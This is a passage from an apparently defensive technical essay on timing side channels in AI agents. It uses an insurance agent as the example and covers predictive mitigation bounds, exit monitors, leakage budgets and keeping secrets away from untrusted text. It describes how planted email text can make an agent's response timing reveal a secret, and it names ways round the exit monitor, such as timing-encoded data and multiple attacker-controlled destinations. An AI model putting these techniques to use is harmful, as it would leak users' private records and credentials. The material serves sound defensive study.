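In a simplified version for the insurance agent, the deadline starts at 30 seconds and doubles after every miss, up to 480, but never comes down again. It can rise only four times, so the complete timing record of $n$ tasks depends only on when those rises happened. This gives $\binom{n+4}{4}$ possible records, and the following limits in bits:

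| Tasks | 16 marks | 5 deadlines, starting again at 30 s for each task | 5 deadlines, never reset |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 4 | 2.3 | 2.3 |
| 10 | 40 | 23 | 10 |
| 100 | 400 | 232 | 22 |
| 1,000 | 4,000 | 2,322 | 35 |

The drawback is that one slow task delays all the later ones. A single email that made the model reason for 250 seconds would raise the deadline to eight minutes until the operator reset it, and each reset would allow more leakage.

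Zhang, Askarov and Myers, in *Predictive Mitigation of Timing Channels for Interactive Systems*, reduce this problem by making separate predictions for different types of request. Each type gets a number of "grace" misses, $l$, that slow only that type. Once it has used them up, its schedule depends on the total number of misses across all types. For $M$ requests of $R$ types and a worst-case time of $T_w$, they limit the leakage to

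$$\log_2(M+1)\,\bigl[(R-1)(l+1) + \log_2(T_w+1) + 1\bigr]\ \text{bits}.$$

The first factor is roughly the information needed to identify which request caused a miss, and the second limits how many misses matter. The total therefore grows with the logarithm of the number of requests.

They tested the method with a proxy between a browser and real websites, five grace misses and a worst case of 300 seconds. One page needed 49 requests, which they grouped in three ways. The bounds below come from putting their settings into the formula, with time in seconds:

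| How they grouped requests | Types | Bound for 100,000 requests | Effect on loading time |
|---|---|---|---|
| By host | 2 | About 250 bits | Almost tripled |
| By host and kind of file | 7 | About 750 bits | About 30% longer |
| Each address separately | 49 | About 4,900 bits | About 30% longer |

Zhang and colleagues recommend the middle option, which they say limits leakage to 850 bits. The finest grouping allows several times as much leakage and is barely faster.

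The timing of an agent's answers would be harder to predict than that of web pages. The mitigator could base its predictions on the type of task if the type is public, but not on the length of the claim record or anything else that depends on a secret. Tasks of the same type might still take anywhere from a few seconds to several minutes, so the schedule would probably settle near the slow end of that range.

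### Combining the schedule with information-flow control

Askarov and colleagues report that their mitigators combine well with other mechanisms for information-flow control (IFC). The mitigator treats the system as a black box and changes only when outputs leave, so it doesn't interfere with labels or policy checks. If IFC makes the text that reaches the insurer the same for every secret, the insurer can learn only from timing and from whether the message arrives. The mitigator limits the timing leak, and a fixed error message at the final deadline could remove the other. Both defences still need IFC, because an email sent on schedule can contain the claim record.

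Zhang, Askarov and Myers (2012) built the idea into a programming language in *Language-based control and mitigation of timing channels*. Any program that passes the language's type checks provably leaks only a bounded amount through timing that an outsider can observe. The proof relies on explicit assumptions about hardware, including how instruction caches behave. *Language Mechanisms for Controlling and Mitigating Timing Channels*, a report on the same work, adds that a model of one suitable hardware design was enough to control timing in some simple but realistic programs.

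An agent's plan could in principle run in such a language. The inference engine would not meet the language's assumptions, because its speed depends on other users' requests and on caches designed to skip work. A mitigator placed where output leaves the agent works without assumptions about the engine, but it limits only what an observer beyond that point can see. Another tenant of the engine could still time the model call directly.

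### A small budget and a one-bit secret

A limit of 35 bits over 1,000 tasks averages 0.035 bits per task, but the leakage may not be spread evenly. Planted text that causes a miss only when a record mentions a dispute can reveal in one task whether the record mentions one, leaving 34 bits of the budget unused.

Even a strict limit on every task protects such a fact only if the limit is extremely small. Suppose a dispute is as likely as not. If the timing of one task may carry 0.1 bits, the attacker's advantage can still reach 0.37. Guaranteeing an advantage of at most 0.1 requires a limit of about 0.007 bits, and repeating the task would raise the advantage again.

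Sun and Xiao therefore assess predictive mitigation by the attacker's advantage instead of by total bits. If no prediction fails, the observer sees the same timing whatever the secret is. For the insurance agent, this means

$$\text{advantage} \le \Pr[\text{miss} \mid \text{dispute}] + \Pr[\text{miss} \mid \text{no dispute}] .$$

If the agent misses its deadline 1% of the time whether or not there is a dispute, the advantage is at most 0.02. If planted text makes it miss nearly every deadline when there is a dispute, the limit is about 1 and gives no protection.

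They tried this on their recordings of vLLM, where the secret was whether another customer's text was in the shared cache. They replayed the recorded response times through a mitigator that doubled its penalty after each miss. Its predictor knew exactly how the attacker had arranged the requests, an advantage that a real service would not have. With the most conservative settings, the results were:

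| Test | Upper limit on the advantage | Extra delay compared with separate caches |
|---|---|---|
| 1,024- and 4,096-token texts, idle engine | 0.074 and 0.028 | 10 to 12 ms |
| 16-token text, requests arranged to fill engine steps exactly | 0.17 | 167 ms |
| 256-token text, same arrangement | 0.32 | 298 ms |
| Engine under load, eight combinations tested | 0.1 in only two of them | 554 and 564 ms in those two |

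The results for long texts on an idle engine are good, but separate caches would close this leak completely and give slightly faster responses. Under load, the delays are much longer and the guarantee usually fails. The requests also asked for only one output token each, which makes this a fairly easy test for a predictor, since the time an agent takes to produce a full answer varies by seconds or minutes. Nobody appears to have repeated the test on an agent.

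### A monitor at the agent's exit

A different approach is to attack the channel and measure how much still gets through. Metere built a monitor through which all of an agent's outgoing messages must pass, along with programs that try to send secrets past it. For each channel, a sender encodes random bits $X$, the monitor processes the messages, and a receiver produces its best guess $Y$. The score for the remaining capacity, known as mutual information, is how much each guess reduces the uncertainty about the bit:

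$$I = H(X) - H(X \mid Y) .$$

Here $H(X)$ is the uncertainty before the guess, in bits, and $H(X \mid Y)$ is the uncertainty left after it. The score is 0 if the guesses are unrelated to the bits and 1 if they are always right. The estimate includes a correction for small samples.

In the timing test, the sender encoded bits in the gaps between messages. Rounding the send times to a grid left about a fifth of the channel's capacity. If errors were equally likely for 0s and 1s, the receiver could still read about 76% of the bits correctly. Releasing messages at a fixed pace reduced the measured capacity to zero.

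That zero depends on how the sender behaves. The monitor keeps messages at least one interval apart, so a sender that tries to go faster produces evenly spaced messages. But a sender that waits two intervals instead of one would leave a visible gap. The monitor can fill gaps with dummy messages, though this is off by default. The dummies could fool an eavesdropper but probably not the insurer, who reads the messages and could see which ones were real.

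The score reflects what one receiver recovered, and a better one might recover more. Metere wrote both the attacks and the defence, and ran 20 trials for each text channel. The default settings, which are meant to avoid disrupting legitimate messages, don't include timing control.

The monitor also keeps a budget of suspicious bits for each destination, which refills over time. A 22-character string in base64, a common way of writing binary data as text, can carry up to 132 bits, so it could hold a whole key. When the budget runs out, the monitor delays or cancels further suspicious messages. But it estimates the bits from a message's text, so it would not count a secret encoded in a delay. An attacker who controls ten websites would also get ten budgets. A budget for each secret would be safer, though the monitor would need to track which secrets could have influenced each message.

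In *Caught in the Act(ivation)*, Chauhan and Revankar (2026) keep a running estimate of how much an agent's replies have revealed about its credentials over a conversation. In a test with 50 synthetic conversations, the running total caught slow leaks that checks on single replies missed. The estimate doesn't cover side channels, and it comes from a learned model and can be too low, so it cannot guarantee that the agent has stayed within its leakage budget. Counting the possible release times is cruder but gives a true upper limit. With a budget of 20 bits, the agent could handle eight tasks at 2.32 bits each before it had to switch to a single fixed deadline.

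### Keeping secrets away from untrusted text

The document attack becomes impossible if no model call that reads untrusted text has access to a secret, because planted text can't make a model's reasoning time depend on a secret the model has never seen. Passwords and access keys can be withheld from the model with almost no loss of function, because the agent has to use them but never has to read them. Chauhan and Revankar note that production agents often place such credentials in the same context as web pages and emails. In their prototype, the real credentials stay in a separate store that only the software running the tools can read, and the model sees decoys that raise an alarm if they appear in its output. *AgenticOS* likewise keeps keys and login cookies in its gateway, which uses them on the agent's behalf.

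The claim record is harder to protect, because the model has to work with its contents. Some tasks can still be split between a model and ordinary code. To check whether the amount in the insurer's email matches the record, one model call can extract the amount from the email as a number, and ordinary code can compare it with the record. The code takes practically the same time whether or not the amounts match. But if the user asks whether the insurer's reasons for refusing the claim fit the facts, a model has to read both together. The user would then have to give up the task, do the comparison personally, or accept a bounded leak.

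No one seems to have measured how many tasks a strict separation would rule out. Tallam and Miller report that CaMeL completes 67% of the tasks in AgentDojo, and they say many of the failures occur because it treats all untrusted data as equally risky. CaMeL still lets a quarantined model read a secret and a stranger's text in the same call, so a rule against this would probably reduce the number of tasks it completes.

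Separation also does not prevent accidental leaks. In the original insurance example, the model that summarises the claim record reads no untrusted text, yet the delay still reveals the dispute unless the agent sends the acknowledgement first or holds it until a fixed release time.
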